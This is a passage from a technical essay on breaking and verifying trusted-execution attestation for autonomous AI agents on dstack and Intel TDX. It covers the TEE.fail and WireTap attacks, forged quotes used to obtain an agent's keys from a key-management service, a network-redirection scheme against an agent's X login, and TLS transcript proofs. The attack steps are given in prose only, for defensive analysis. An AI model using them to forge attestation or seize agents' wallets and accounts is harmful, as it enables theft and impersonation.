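| Attack | Processors | Cost of equipment | What the researchers obtained |
|---|---|---|---|
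| WireTap | Intel SGX servers with DDR4 memory | Under $1,000 | An SGX attestation key |
| Battering RAM | Intel SGX and AMD SEV-SNP servers with DDR4 memory | Under €50 | Access to protected memory, which on SGX they could both read and change |
| TEE.fail | Intel SGX and TDX and AMD SEV-SNP servers with DDR5 memory | Under $1,000 | The key behind a machine's SGX and TDX quotes, and keys from individual programs |

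TEE.fail matters most here because dstack agents run under TDX, Intel's technology for confidential virtual machines (CVMs). SEV-SNP is AMD's equivalent. In *TEE.fail*, Chuang, Seto and colleagues tested fifth-generation Intel Xeon and AMD Zen 5 machines. They bought parts second-hand, whereas earlier work had put the cost of such a setup at around $170,000. Intel's 2025 security notice, also titled *TEE.fail*, also lists fourth-generation Xeon and Xeon 6 processors.

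Accounts differ on how long the attack takes. The post *Physical integrity, attestation, and the state of permissionless TEEs* gives about 15 minutes, and Schneier on Security's *New Attacks Against Secure Enclaves* (2025) gives three minutes. The latter adds that the attacker must compromise the operating-system kernel. That is an obstacle for an outsider who gains physical access to the server, but a deployer who owns the server already controls the host's kernel.

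Chuang and colleagues write that they could break TDX's guarantees for every application that relies on dstack. They tried this on a tool for hosting Jupyter notebooks and a front end for a language model. Both passed attestation while running without an enclave. They also passed NVIDIA's attestation for confidential graphics processors, using evidence from a different computer. A deployer could do the same to claim that a particular model writes the agent's posts on protected hardware.

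The researchers also attacked BuilderNet, a system for assembling Ethereum blocks. Flashbots, which helps run it, objected that the researchers had used a non-production copy in a lab, which did not represent the production system's security. That objection is fair for servers in guarded buildings, but a deployer who hosts the agent in their own office has the same access to the machine that the researchers had.

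### Reading one agent's secrets

The deployer can attack the agent's own program. Chuang and colleagues took a private key from the enclave of a node on Secret, a blockchain for confidential contracts, and used it to obtain the network's master key, without needing the machine's attestation key. On an AMD server, they recovered signing keys from OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library, inside a CVM. An agent's wallet key also signs messages, and TDX encrypts memory deterministically, as the AMD server does, so a deployer with an interposer can probably recover the wallet key.

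A random password may be harder to read this way. Intel describes WireTap as building a dictionary of ciphertexts for "low entropy data", meaning data with few possible values, and a random 20-character password has far too many possible values for that. But if the program saved the password to disk, the deployer needs only the disk key to read it, and may be able to get that key from the KMS with a forged quote.

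### Signing quotes for programs that never ran in an enclave

Reading an agent's memory requires access to the agent's machine. With a stolen attestation key, a deployer can instead impersonate an enclave from anywhere.

Intel certifies a key for each machine, the Provisioning Certification Key, which is used to certify the key that signs the machine's quotes. Chuang and colleagues extracted this key from a TDX machine whose status was "UpToDate", the highest level of trust. They could then certify their own signing keys and sign any quote. According to *Physical integrity, attestation, and the state of permissionless TEEs*, one of their forged quotes contained nonsensical measurements and still passed Intel's standard verification.

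Suppose a deployer has such a key and wants Ada to send money to a wallet on the deployer's laptop. The deployer can choose both the measurements and the report data in a quote. They copy the measurements of the honest program, write a matching event log and compute *h* for the laptop's wallet. When Ada sends her challenge *c*, the deployer puts *h* ‖ *c* into the report data and signs the quote.

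All seven of Ada's checks succeed, and the laptop can also sign *c* because it has the wallet key. The only thing the deployer can't invent is the processor's identity, because the certificate belongs to the machine they took the key from. To catch this, Ada would have to know which machines to accept.

The post names ElizaOS among the projects that use on-chain quote verification from a company called Automata. It reports that a forged quote passed this verification on a test network. Some projects add their own restrictions, such as lists of permitted operators, but those that rely on the quote alone accept forged quotes.

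### What a forged quote gets from the KMS

A KMS that releases keys on the strength of a quote can make the same mistake as Ada. The agent's own machine can be in a guarded data centre, out of the deployer's reach:

1. The deployer extracts an attestation key from some other TDX machine that they own.
2. They forge a quote with the agent's approved measurements and compose hash.
3. The KMS accepts the quote and releases the agent's keys to the deployer.
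4. The deployer computes the wallet key. If they also have a copy of the agent's encrypted disk, they can read the saved passwords.

Unlike the approval of a leaky version, this theft leaves no trace in the DstackApp contract, because the forged quote's compose hash is already on the list.

The contract's list of allowed machines could prevent the theft at the third step, but only if the list names particular machines and the KMS takes the machine's identity from Intel's certificate, ignoring any identifier that the applicant can write. Allowing any machine removes this protection, but that setting is what keeps an agent running through firmware maintenance after its deployer has given up the contract. An agent whose code nobody can change may therefore be especially exposed to forged quotes.

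An attacker with a forged quote can also pose as a KMS node. WireTap describes a similar attack on Secret's test network, in which the researchers joined with a forged attestation and received the network's secret seed. dstack's KMS would be similarly exposed if it copied its root key to such an impostor.

Splitting the root key among several nodes, so that *t* of them are needed, contains only some of this damage:

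| What the attacker does | Root key copied to every node | Root key split with threshold *t* |
|---|---|---|
| Reads the memory of one KMS node | Gets every application's keys | Gets one share |
| Joins as a false KMS node | Gets every application's keys | Gets one share for each false node |
| Requests an agent's keys with a forged quote | Gets that agent's keys | Gets that agent's keys |
| Reads the agent's own memory | Gets the secrets used there | Gets the secrets used there |

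In the third row, the honest nodes together derive the key and give it to the wrong party. The outcome in the second row also depends on which nodes may join. One stolen attestation key can sign quotes for *t* nodes that don't exist, so the KMS should give each physical machine at most one share and admit only known machines. WireTap similarly recommends that networks require further permission before trusting a node.

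### What the manufacturers and Phala replied

Intel considers these attacks outside the scope of its memory encryption, and cites a 2021 document that already said so. It did not plan to issue a CVE, an entry in the public catalogue of security flaws. An optional integrity mode on fifth-generation Xeon and Xeon 6 processors adds protection against attacks like Battering RAM, but Intel doesn't present it as a fix for passive reading, the method TEE.fail uses. AMD's *Compromising Trusted Execution Environments through DDR5 Memory Bus Interposition* (2025) also puts physical attacks out of scope and announces no mitigations.

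No update can repair the machines already in use. Intel told Chuang and colleagues that microcode, the updatable code inside a processor, can't change the memory encryption engine. Intel's older SGX design for desktop computers produced different ciphertext on every write and resisted this kind of attack. *TEE Anchor* (September 2026) notes that Intel has discontinued that design, partly for performance reasons, and concludes that waiting for a robust hardware fix is not realistic.

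Phala was one of the four SGX-based networks in the WireTap study. It said in *Phala Announces Strategic Transition Beyond SGX in Response to WireTap Findings*, on 30 September 2025, that it would shut down its SGX machines and move to TDX, which it described as "hardened against physical bus-level attacks". Four weeks later, TEE.fail showed that TDX was not hardened against these attacks.

Phala said in a statement on 28 October 2025 that its servers were in guarded data centres and that there was "no feasible path" for the attack. This is a reasonable argument about an interposer on Phala's own machines, though it depends on trusting every technician who can reach them. Guarding those machines doesn't prevent someone from forging a quote with a different machine, so Phala's KMS also has to reject unfamiliar processors. Phala says that each of its servers is bound to a hardware identifier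 and that anyone can verify that workloads run only on listed processors, but Ada needs to confirm that the KMS refuses to release keys to unlisted ones. The statement doesn't cover an agent running on its deployer's own dstack server.

### Checks that tie a quote to a data centre

Intel advises people who rely on a platform to understand its physical protection, and says that owners can identify which machines they control. A lockout requires less of a data centre than many other uses of enclaves. The lockout holds even if the operator reads the agent's memory, or a government orders it to, as long as the deployer never gets the secrets.

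In 2026 these checks varied by host, according to the *Physical integrity* post, whose author works at Ritual, a company that uses dstack. Microsoft's Azure supplied a signature showing that a CVM ran in its cloud, but its quote measured Microsoft's software layer instead of the customer's operating system. Amazon's Nitro enclaves came with Amazon's signature but didn't encrypt memory. Google offered no such signature for TDX machines, though it was reportedly working on one, so somebody could boot Google's published firmware in a basement and obtain the same kind of quote. Ordinary hosting companies such as OVH, whose servers Phala uses, didn't provide a signature either.

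Intel has designed a standard remedy, the Platform Ownership Endorsement, in which a hosting company signs the identifier of each processor it controls. When the post appeared, Intel hadn't yet released the software for it. Resetting the machine gives it a new identifier and invalidates old endorsements. Otherwise, a deployer could extract a machine's key at home, rent rack space for it in a respectable data centre, and go on forging quotes that appear to come from there.

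Proof of Cloud, a joint effort that includes Phala, works without signatures from hosting companies. At its first level, people check that particular machines are under a provider's control. The second level would link the quote cryptographically to a separate security chip in the data centre, and the third would monitor machines continuously. Only the first was operating in 2026, and the public register of machines had no interface for outsiders to search it. Ada would have to ask who inspected the agent's machine and when, and whether anyone could have moved it since. She should prefer inspectors from outside Phala, because otherwise Phala would be vouching for its own servers.

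*TEE Anchor* also proposes that organisations endorse machines. None of these methods secures the lockout if the deployer hosts the agent at the office, because an honest inspection would show only that the deployer can reach the memory.

### Attacks that don't require opening the machine

Guards are less useful against software attacks. Researchers keep finding side channels in TDX. *Proof of Cloud* (2025), a paper about tying CVMs to data centres, cites recent work on cache attacks and on running an enclave one instruction at a time. Manufacturers can often fix such flaws with microcode and then mark unpatched machines as out of date, which is why Ada checks the patch level.

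That check can fail if the attacker has the secret from which a processor derives its attestation keys. *Insecure Despite Proven Updated* (May 2026) reported a software-only way to extract this secret from AMD's EPYC Milan server processors. The attack doesn't affect Intel TDX. But Zhou and colleagues designed dstack to run on AMD hardware as well, and a KMS that accepted quotes from Milan machines might release keys to someone who forged a quote without using an interposer.

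A host can also attack a CVM through ACPI tables, which describe the hardware to the operating system and contain small programs that the kernel runs. In an attack called BadAML, these programs read and alter the CVM's private memory. A correctly configured TDX machine measures the tables into RTMR0, so Ada would detect a change when she compared the boot measurements. But *Physical integrity* says that Google publishes no signed reference values for its tables. If an agent depends on a KMS in Google's cloud, as in *Nitro-KMS Walkthrough*, Ada may have nothing to compare the tables' measurements with.

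### Can the agent recover?

dstack's designers expected enclaves to fail. Zhou and colleagues write that hardware can be compromised, and they offer key rotation and migration to other machines as the remedy. In *Key Management Protocol For Decentralized Root-of-Trust*, the early draft of the design, each machine regularly receives new keys for its stored data and deletes the old ones. Somebody who breaks in on Wednesday can't use Wednesday's keys to read what the agent sealed on Monday. If the KMS then stops sending keys to that machine, they can't read Friday's data either.

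The compromised machine has to be identified before the KMS can exclude it. The draft leaves detection out of scope, and KU Leuven warns that the Battering RAM attack may leave no trace. Rotating the keys without excluding the machine achieves little, because a deployer with a working attestation key can request each new set.

Even a well-timed rotation doesn't recall copied secrets that other systems still accept:

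| Secret the deployer copied | Is it useless after a new root key? | What else has to happen |
|---|---|---|
| Disk key | For newly encrypted data, but not for old copies of the disk | Nothing can protect the old copies |
| Wallet key | No | The agent must move the money before the deployer does |
| Email or X password | No | The program must change it and repeat the takeover checks |
| OAuth token | No | The program must revoke the app's access |
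| Machine's attestation key | No | The KMS and outside verifiers must reject that machine |

Suppose a deployer copies an agent's email and X passwords on 1 March, and the KMS replaces its root key on 1 April. On 2 April both services still accept the old passwords, so the deployer can change them and lock the agent out. If the agent derives its passwords from an application key, as in Marlin's design, and the deployer has stolen that key, increasing the counter does not help because the deployer can compute the next password too.

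Recovery has to happen in the right order, as the original takeover did. First, the KMS has to exclude the compromised machine and replace any stolen root or application key, and the agent has to restart on hardware that the deployer can't reach. The agent should then change the mailbox password, secure the X account and move the money. If it does these things while still on the deployer's server, the deployer may be able to copy the new secrets too. The deployer can also act first at any point, and has an advantage if nobody else knows about the theft.

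Followers also need a reliable way to learn the new wallet address. A signature from the old wallet can no longer confirm it, because the deployer can sign an announcement that directs payments to their own wallet. A post on X is also unreliable if the deployer may still have the password. Ada would need a fresh quote for the new key, from a machine that someone she trusts has put where the deployer can't access it.

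## What evidence can show that the passwords were changed?

A program that has taken over an X account can't prove that it changed the password by showing people the new one, because anyone who saw it could use it. The change happened on X's servers, which the enclave doesn't measure and outsiders can't inspect. A password also has no public half that Ada can look for in a quote, as she can with a wallet key.

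tee_hee_he's program requested a quote right after it reset the X password, and put the name of the X account into the report data. Nous Research reasoned that the enclave could produce a quote with this name only once the agent was the account's sole owner. But any program can write a username into that field, so the name is evidence only if the program had to complete the takeover before requesting the quote.

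### From a username to a changed password

The inference from the quote to the changed password has four premises:

1. The published code ran in a genuine enclave.
2. Nothing in that enclave requests a quote with the account's name until every step of that account's takeover has succeeded.
3. The program was connected to the real X.
4. X's replies meant what the code took them to mean.

If all four are true, X accepted a password that the enclave generated. They don't show that the password is still secret, because the program might have printed it afterward.

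The first premise requires a link between the source code Ada reads and the image that ran. A reproducible build provides one. *Verifying TEE Applications* describes an alternative for dstack, in which the whole build runs inside a CVM from an exact version of the source code, and a quote covers the finished image. This is easier for developers, who don't have to make every build come out identical. But Ada can't repeat the build and compare the results, so she has to trust a second enclave and the compiler inside it.

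The second premise depends on the order of steps in the code. That order is in doubt for tee_hee_he because its quote may predate the removal of the phone number and connected apps. Ada also has to consider what else in the CVM can request quotes. The part of tee_hee_he's configuration file that Phala published gives the agent's container access to the guest agent, so any code in that container could have requested a quote with the account's name.

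The account name could be wrong. If the program gets it from an environment variable, a deployer can let the program take over a throwaway account and set the variable to a well-known account's name. The program should instead read the name from X after logging in. It should also read the account's numeric ID, because a user can rename an account and somebody else can then register the old name.

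The third premise is in doubt because the host operator carries all of the enclave's network traffic. An operator who is also the deployer could try this:

1. They direct the program's connection to a copy of X's website on their own server.
2. The program logs in to the copy and changes the password there. The copy reports success, but nothing has changed on the real X.
3. On the real X, the deployer authorises the app and obtains an OAuth token. They pass it to the program through the copy.
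4. The program requests its quote and starts posting with a token that works, while the deployer still has the real password.

TLS prevents this if the program itself checks, inside the enclave, that the website's certificate is for X's domain and comes from an authority it trusts. Browser-automation tools commonly have a setting that ignores certificate errors. If the measured code uses that setting, or the image trusts an additional certificate authority that the deployer controls, the quote doesn't show that the password was changed. The program has to make the same check when it connects to the email provider.

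The fourth premise is the hardest to establish, because the program has only web pages to go on. If its code treats the absence of an error message as success, it may count a page that stopped loading or a request for a security code as a successful change. A better test is to log out, log in with the new password, and then try the old one in a separate session. A clear message that the old password is wrong is good evidence, but a notice about too many attempts isn't, since X might show it for a correct password too.

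Even a well-tested program has access only to what X shows its users. A TLS transcript proof could let Ada examine a reply herself, but she would still depend on X to report the account's state correctly. Nous Research suggests that platforms could run part of their login systems in attested enclaves. Ada could then check the code that keeps the account record, and would not need to infer as much about its contents from web pages.

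### Where a deployment fault breaks the argument

The table matches common faults to the premises.

| Fault | Premise that may fail | Why |
|---|---|---|
| Container image named by a tag | The published code ran | Somebody can substitute a program that requests the quote at once |
| Pre-launch script that downloads code | The published code ran | The download can alter the program |
| Stolen attestation key | The published code ran | The deployer can write the whole quote |
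| Development image, or a container with a shell | Nothing requests the quote early | A person who logs in can request it |
| Second container with access to the guest agent | Nothing requests the quote early | It can put any account's name in a quote |
| Variable that sets the account's name | Nothing requests the quote early | The takeover may have involved a different account |
| Variable that sets a proxy, web address or trusted certificate | The program reached the real X | It may have connected to the deployer's server |
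| Outdated code for reading X's pages | X's replies meant what the code assumed | The program may take a missing page for an empty list |
| Public logs | None | The password changed, but the deployer may be able to read the new one |
| KMS without update rules | None | The password changed, but a later version can read it from the disk |

### Can anyone still check tee_hee_he's quote?

Nous Research's post has "TODO" where readers would expect links to the quote, the Docker image and the virtual machine's image. Other pages provide these links. The README from Nous Research and Teleport gives addresses for the quote (quote.hex) and the Docker image. Phala's *We Know the Truth of AI Agent* (2024), published the day after the launch, links to version 0.1.0 of the dstack base image.

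Phala also checked the quote by replaying RTMR3 from three hashes, covering the root filesystem, the configuration file and a certificate. The result matched the value in the quote. The configuration file names the agent's image by its digest, so the quote should identify one exact image.

However, Phala couldn't publish the whole configuration file because it contained API keys. It instead offered a zero-knowledge proof, which shows that a computation on hidden data gave a certain result. The proof showed that the file had the hash recorded in the quote and that the expected image line appeared at a particular position. It did not cover the rest of the file, including the startup arguments and variables, so the file could have listed a second container with its own access to the guest agent.

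In Phala's decoded quote, the boot measurements RTMR1 and RTMR2 are all zeros, which means that nothing had been recorded in them. Phala says that RTMR0 to RTMR2 cover the kernel and the startup filesystem, so RTMR0 would have to cover both, unless MRTD does. Phala doesn't explain the zeros or print MRTD in the post. If no register covered the startup software, that software could have recorded a false hash for the root filesystem. Phala suggests relaunching the image and comparing the registers, but a second launch could produce the same zeros and still not show whether any register covered the startup software.

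Phala's check is thus good evidence that a file mentioning the right image was in the CVM. It is weaker evidence about the account, because the post shows only the four RTMR values and not the decoded report data, which should contain the username. Ada would have to decode quote.hex herself to check for it.

She would also have to confirm that the image was built from the published source code. According to Phala's timeline, the developers published the code about four hours after the agent appeared on 29 October 2024. A public index shows that the repository changed again on 7 November, so Ada would need the version from launch day. Phala wrote at the time that the base image was not yet fully reproducible, and encouraged developers to make their Docker images so "in the future". Without a reproducible build, she would have to inspect the compiled program, which takes far more skill than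 reading its source.

All of this depends on somebody keeping the files online. If Docker Hub no longer serves an image with the published digest, the quote identifies a program that nobody can examine. A newer agent can avoid some of these problems, because dstack's release notes for version 0.5.9 describe its guest images as reproducible and include a script for rebuilding them. Its developers should still archive the source, image, configuration file, event log and quote together.

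### A record that Ada can read

A username fills only a small part of the report data, and Ada has to work out everything else from the code. The program could instead write a longer record and put its hash in the report data. Phala lists a hash of the application's state among the common uses of report data. Lit Protocol's service already does something similar, supplying one quote with empty report data for checking the software and another whose report data is the hash of a file listing the checksums of its TLS certificates.

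Suppose that Magpie, the invented agent with the faulty configuration, has been relaunched correctly and has taken over its X account again. Ada sends it 32 random bytes, and it returns this record with a quote:

```yaml
record: account-control-v1
service: x.com
account: magpie
account_id: 1840000000000000001
wallet: solana:<public key>
last_deployer_contact_removed: 2026-10-05T12:10Z
password_set: 2026-10-05T13:20Z
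settings_checked: 2026-10-05T13:25Z
recent_block: <hash of an Ethereum block>
new_password: accepted
old_password: rejected
linked_email: controlled by this program
linked_phone: none
passkeys: none
delegates: none
other_sessions: 0
connected_apps: [magpie-poster]
challenge: <Ada's 32 bytes>
```

The program computes

d = SHA-256(record) ‖ 32 zero bytes

and uses *d* as the report data. Ada hashes the text exactly as she received it, compares the result with the first half of *d*, and looks for her challenge in the last line. Because the challenge is part of the record, the quote ties it to the account and the wallet as well. She can also ask Magpie to sign the record with its wallet key.

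X's reset codes expire after 60 minutes. Magpie set its final password 70 minutes after removing the deployer's last contact details, so any code the deployer had requested before then should have expired. Ada can also see a developer app called magpie-poster in the list of connected apps, and she can ask who owns it.

Even a detailed record is not evidence if its values are fixed text in the program. A program written to print "other_sessions: 0" will print that no matter how many sessions are open. Ada therefore has to find the code that produces each line and confirm that it takes the value from X. As with the wallet key, the challenge should be the only input the program accepts from outside.

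The host operator may be able to influence the program's clock, so Ada should check that the "secure_time" setting in dstack's configuration file is switched on. The block hash provides a separate check, but it shows only that Magpie made the record after that block, not how long after.

### Events, logs and signed posts

Such a record can also go in RTMR3, where software can add events but can't remove them. zkSecurity's 2025 audit describes a guest-agent function, EmitEvent, that lets an application add its own events. Magpie could use it to add the hash of its takeover record, and every later quote from the same run would then cover that event, even quotes requested for other purposes. Phala could reproduce the RTMR3 value in tee_hee_he's quote from the three startup hashes alone, so that quote covered no such event.

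Events are particularly useful for recording bad news. tee_hee_he's program could have added an event just before it released its credentials, and every later quote from that run would have reflected it. But RTMR3 resets to zero when the machine restarts, so a host operator can clear the history. After a restart, the program should repeat its checks before it adds a new takeover event.

*Runtime Attestation* describes a comparable function in which the caller gives each event a domain, an operation and some content. For Magpie these might be "x.com", "password-change" and the hash of the record. The labels help a reader understand the event but don't identify the caller. In dstack, any container that can reach the guest agent could presumably add an event with the same labels, so Ada has to check which containers have that access.

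She also needs to confirm that the event belongs to RTMR3. An event log can contain entries for several registers, and a verifier that replays only RTMR3 might accept a false entry listed under another one. *fix(node): enforce RTMR3 validation on event checks* (2025) changed one node program in August 2025 so that it looks for the configuration hash only among RTMR3's entries.

A public log survives restarts. For Bobu's magic show, Sun and colleagues recorded events on the Arbitrum blockchain, including the X account's ID and the post. Magpie could publish the hash of each takeover record in the same way, signed with its attested key, and keep the full text somewhere public. The block hash inside the record then gives the earliest time Magpie could have made it, and the log entry gives the latest. The deployer can't quietly withdraw an entry, but they may be able to stop new ones from leaving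 the machine, so Ada can't assume the log is complete.

Magpie could also post a short statement on X with its account name, wallet address and the date, signed with the wallet key. A Solana signature takes 64 bytes, or 88 characters in a common text encoding, which fits in an ordinary post. Unlike the quote, the statement appears on the account itself, so it would reveal an honest mistake in the account's name. But a deployer who still has access to the account can copy the signed text and post it by hand, so the statement doesn't show that only the program controls the account.

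| Evidence | What it adds | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Quote with only the account's name | Ties the name to the measured program | Contains no time, results or wallet key |
| Quote with a hashed record | Ties the results to the wallet key and Ada's challenge | Ada needs the exact text and has to check how the program produced it |
| Event in RTMR3 | Appears in every later quote from the same run | A restart clears it |
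| Entry in a public log | Gives everyone the same lasting history | The host operator can hold entries back |
| Signed post on X | Links the key to the account from X's side | Anyone who can post from the account can publish or delete it |

A hashed record with a public log entry seems best for most agents. Adding an event is useful if the agent also issues quotes for other purposes.

### A moment and a state

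Ada wants to know whether Magpie's deployer is locked out today. A quote describes the moment when the program requested it, and its signature stays valid long after circumstances change. For example, somebody who downloaded tee_hee_he's quote in December 2024 would have found the same report data as on launch day, although the program should have printed the credentials for its developers about a month earlier.

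Ada can ask for a new quote every day, but what she learns depends on what the program does before requesting it. If the program copies yesterday's results and inserts her new challenge, she learns only that it is still running. If it logs in again, she also learns that nobody has replaced the password. It has to reread the settings to find a newly linked phone number or an additional session. The record should therefore state when the program last checked each item.

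Regular checks can miss a brief intrusion. Suppose that a deployer uses a hidden way into the account for *L* minutes and then removes every trace. If the program checks the settings once at a random moment in each period of *T* minutes, and the intrusion falls within one period, the chance of detecting it is

P = L / T

Daily checks have a 10/1,440, or 0.7 per cent, chance of catching a ten-minute intrusion. Hourly checks raise the chance to 17 per cent. A deployer who intruded for ten minutes on 100 different days would have about an even chance of escaping daily checks every time.

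The real chance may be lower, because a deployer who is also the host operator can watch the network traffic to see when a check has finished, or pause the CVM during the intrusion. Ada can't prevent a pause, but she can notice one if Magpie has promised a record every six hours and none arrives. She should then treat the lockout as unconfirmed. The cause may be an ordinary outage, but the next record won't show what happened in between, even if it looks normal.

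More frequent checks also have drawbacks. Nous Research preferred the OAuth token partly because it expected constant browser use to be more likely to trigger X's anomaly detection. A program that logs in every hour may get its account locked, and the checks have to stay within X's rules on automation. These limits could mean checking less often than Ada would like.

Some kinds of access would go undetected no matter how many checks there were. A copied backup code changes nothing on the settings page until somebody uses it, and an email provider's employee can read a message without leaving a trace the program can detect. For these cases, Ada has to rely on how the program set up the account.

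### If a post appears that the program didn't write

Magpie could enter the hash of each post in the public log before publishing it, so that anyone could compare the log with the account's posts. If it published first, a network failure before it made the entry would leave a genuine post without one. Nous Research mentions signing every post as a simpler way to identify an agent's messages, and this would allow a similar comparison.

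Suppose a post advertising a new cryptocurrency appears on Magpie's account on 12 October without a log entry. The deployer may have kept an old token, a stranger might have stolen one, somebody at X might have interfered, or a fault in Magpie might have let it publish without logging the post. The post doesn't show who was responsible, even if the deployer owns a large amount of the advertised currency.

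Such a post does damage the claim that only the program can act. Unless the fault was in Magpie, somebody outside the enclave could post, and that person may already have had access when earlier records showed no problem. If so, those records correctly describe what the program found, but its checks missed something. Magpie should look for such posts itself and, if it finds one, publish a warning, revoke its connected apps and repeat the takeover.

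Missing posts are harder to interpret. If the log has an entry but X has no matching post, somebody may have deleted the post, X may have removed it, or Magpie may have failed to publish it. The program can rule out the last possibility by recording the post's address once it appears. Comparing the log with public posts would not reveal whether the deployer had read or sent private messages.

A year without an unexplained post is only weak evidence of a lockout, because a careful deployer might save their access for one profitable occasion. The log makes that access risky to use, since a single unexplained post could expose it. The log gives no protection against a deployer who controls the model's answers, because the program would log and sign the resulting posts as its own.

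### Emails, statements and screenshots

Many agents have no attested record, so their deployers offer other evidence. None of it comes close to showing that the deployer is locked out, but some of it is stronger than the rest.

An original confirmation email from X is probably the most useful evidence. Mail servers commonly sign outgoing messages, and Ada can check the signature against a key published for the sender's domain if she has the complete message and the key is still available. A valid signature would show that X sent a notice about this account on that date, but not who chose the new password, since the deployer could have changed it by hand. A picture of the email is much less valuable because it lacks the signature.

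A statement by the deployer comes next if it is specific. Ada can investigate each claim in a dated statement that names the owner of the developer app, the administrator of the mailbox and everyone who ever knew the password, but "The agent is fully autonomous" is too vague to test. If one claim turns out to be false, she has good reason to doubt the others.

Screenshots are the weakest of the three. The deployer can change the text of a web page in their own browser before taking one, and even a genuine screenshot leaves out the other settings pages. A recent, genuine screenshot of the account's security settings can even be evidence against the lockout, because if the program didn't take it, somebody outside the enclave was logged in to the account.

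## Can proofs of TLS sessions show the state of an account?

Instead of a screenshot, Ada might ask Magpie for a copy of the settings page that neither the program nor the deployer could have altered. TLS transcript proofs, which companies also sell as zkTLS or web proofs, come close to this. They can show that a particular website sent certain text over an encrypted connection, while hiding the parts that should stay secret.

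### Why an ordinary recording proves nothing

When a browser connects to X, both sides derive the same secret key, *k*. The server uses it to encrypt each reply and to compute a tag, a kind of checksum:

t = MAC(k, reply)

If someone on the network changes the reply, the tag no longer matches. But the browser also has *k*, so its owner can write a reply that lists no phone number, compute a matching tag and claim that X sent it. TLSNotary's *Frequently Asked Questions* gives this as the reason TLS guarantees authenticity only to the two ends of the connection. The server signs its temporary public key at the start, which shows that it took part in a connection, but the signature doesn't cover any of the page's text.

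Zero-knowledge proofs don't solve this on their own. *DECO* (Zhang, Maram and colleagues, 2019) considers a simple scheme in which the client records the encrypted traffic and proves that it decrypts to a reply with valid tags. The scheme fails because the client could have invented the reply and encrypted it. Somebody else has to witness the session by taking part in it, and TLSNotary's *Zero-knowledge ≠ trustless* (2026) stresses that this witness can't be added afterwards. If Magpie took over its account last month without a witness, it can prove what the settings page contains today but not what it contained then.

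### A notary with a share of the key

DECO's solution is to withhold part of the key from the client until the client has handed over the server's reply. TLSNotary, an open-source project from a research lab of the Ethereum Foundation, uses the same approach. The client, here Magpie's program, is called the prover, and the witness is called the verifier, or the notary if it acts on other people's behalf.

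TLS uses an elliptic curve to agree on a key, but this example uses ordinary numbers to show how the prover and the notary share it. The public number *G* is 2.

- X picks the secret 3 and sends 3 × 2 = 6.
- The notary picks the secret 5 and gives Magpie 5 × 2 = 10.
- Magpie picks the secret 4, computes 4 × 2 = 8, adds the notary's 10 and sends X the sum, 18.
- X computes 3 × 18 = 54, the shared secret.
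- Magpie can compute 4 × 6 = 24 and the notary 5 × 6 = 30. Together these make 54, but neither party knows the other's part.

With ordinary numbers, Magpie could find the notary's secret by dividing 10 by 2. Nobody knows a practical way to do the equivalent on the curve. X notices nothing unusual, because it receives one public key and follows the normal procedure. The session then continues in five steps:

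1. Magpie and the notary derive the session keys through two-party computation, which lets two parties calculate a result together without showing each other their inputs. Each gets one share of the key.
2. They encrypt Magpie's request together, and X sends its encrypted reply.
3. Magpie gives the notary the encrypted reply and commits to its own key share. A commitment is typically a hash of some data and a random number, which fixes the data without revealing it. Committing to the share matters because, with the widely used cipher AES-GCM, someone who knows the key can find a second key that decrypts the same bytes to different text.
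4. The notary releases its share. Magpie can now read the reply, but it is too late to change it.
5. The notary signs commitments to the exchange. Magpie can later reveal selected parts and prove that they match.

According to TLSNotary, the notary sees when the session took place, how long the messages were, how many round trips they needed and which cipher the two sides used. It doesn't see the text or learn which website Magpie contacted.

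If Ada is the verifier herself, she doesn't have to trust a notary, but the result convinces only her. Anyone else would have to trust that she didn't collude with Magpie's deployer, because together they would have both shares of the key and could invent any reply. They would have to trust a professional notary in the same way. TLSNotary's *Introduction* suggests requiring signatures from several notaries, so that a dishonest prover would have to corrupt more than one. Grigor and colleagues also mention splitting a single notary's role among several organisations, but TLSNotary's developers say this is not yet practical.

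### A proxy that records the traffic

The notary can also sit between the prover and the website and record the traffic it forwards. Allen and colleagues trace this method to DECO as well. TLSNotary's *Introducing Proxy Mode* (2026) describes a version that works as follows:

1. Magpie opens an ordinary TLS session with X through the notary, which records the encrypted traffic but can't read it.
2. When the session ends, Magpie proves in zero knowledge that it knows the master secret from which the session keys come.
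3. It also proves that these keys correctly decrypt the "Finished" messages, in which both sides confirm the handshake. Only a participant in that handshake could know a secret that passes this test.
4. The notary checks the tags on X's recorded replies under the same keys, and Magpie reveals the parts it wants to show.

Magpie has the whole key throughout the session, so the method relies on the notary receiving the replies directly from X. Someone who controls the network between the notary and X could let X complete the handshake and then replace X's replies with text encrypted under Magpie's key. A colluding notary could do the same. An agent's deployer often controls the agent's network, but should find it much harder to control an independent notary's connection to X.

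X sees the notary's network address instead of Magpie's. X may block data-centre addresses, and a logged-in session that suddenly appears at a new address may look like a hijacking. Allen and colleagues report that the company zkPass uses a proxy by default and falls back on joint computation for websites that don't support the proxy. Reclaim Protocol's *Proxying Is Enough* defends a proxy design in which the witness attests to the encrypted request and reply, and a zero-knowledge proof reveals part of the text.

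### An enclave that fetches the page

A third kind of witness is a program in an enclave that logs in to the website, reads the page and signs what it finds. An attestation quote ties the signing key to the program. *πCreds* (2026) traces this design to the Town Crier system and points out that one attestation can cover both fetching the data and processing it. Companies often sell these services as zkTLS too, but Allen and colleagues call that name a misnomer because the services use no zero-knowledge proofs.

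Magpie already works this way when it reads its settings and puts the hash of a takeover record in a quote. A second enclave, run by somebody else, would give Ada separate evidence. But Magpie would have to send that enclave its session cookie, the secret that keeps a browser logged in. If the enclave leaked the cookie, the deployer might be able to use it to get back into the account. With either of the other methods, the cookie stays with Magpie.

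Enclaves are attractive because they are fast. TLSNotary's *Where does your trust live?* (2026) reports that Peer, a service for exchanging ordinary money and cryptocurrency, cut the time for its payment checks from about thirty seconds to under one second by moving them from zkTLS to Amazon's Nitro Enclaves. TLSNotary's developers, who admit they aren't neutral, object that users' privacy now depends on a chip maker's attestation. The objection has some merit for an agent's account, because the private data includes a key to the account.

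### Costs and TLS versions

*Proxy mode benchmarks* (TLSNotary, 2026) compares TLSNotary's two modes on simulated home and mobile connections, with a 1 KB request and a 2 KB reply. The table gives the results for programs running outside a browser. The enclave figures aren't directly comparable because they come from Grigor and colleagues, who sent requests to language models through an enclave.

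| | Joint computation | Recording proxy | Enclave |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whom an outsider trusts | The notary | The notary and its network connection to the website | The chip maker, the machine's guards and the program that fetches the page |
| What breaks the proof | The notary colludes with the prover | The same, or an accomplice controls that connection | A stolen attestation key or a faulty program |
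| TLS versions | 1.2 in TLSNotary; 1.3 in a research prototype | 1.2 in TLSNotary's published design | Any that the program supports |
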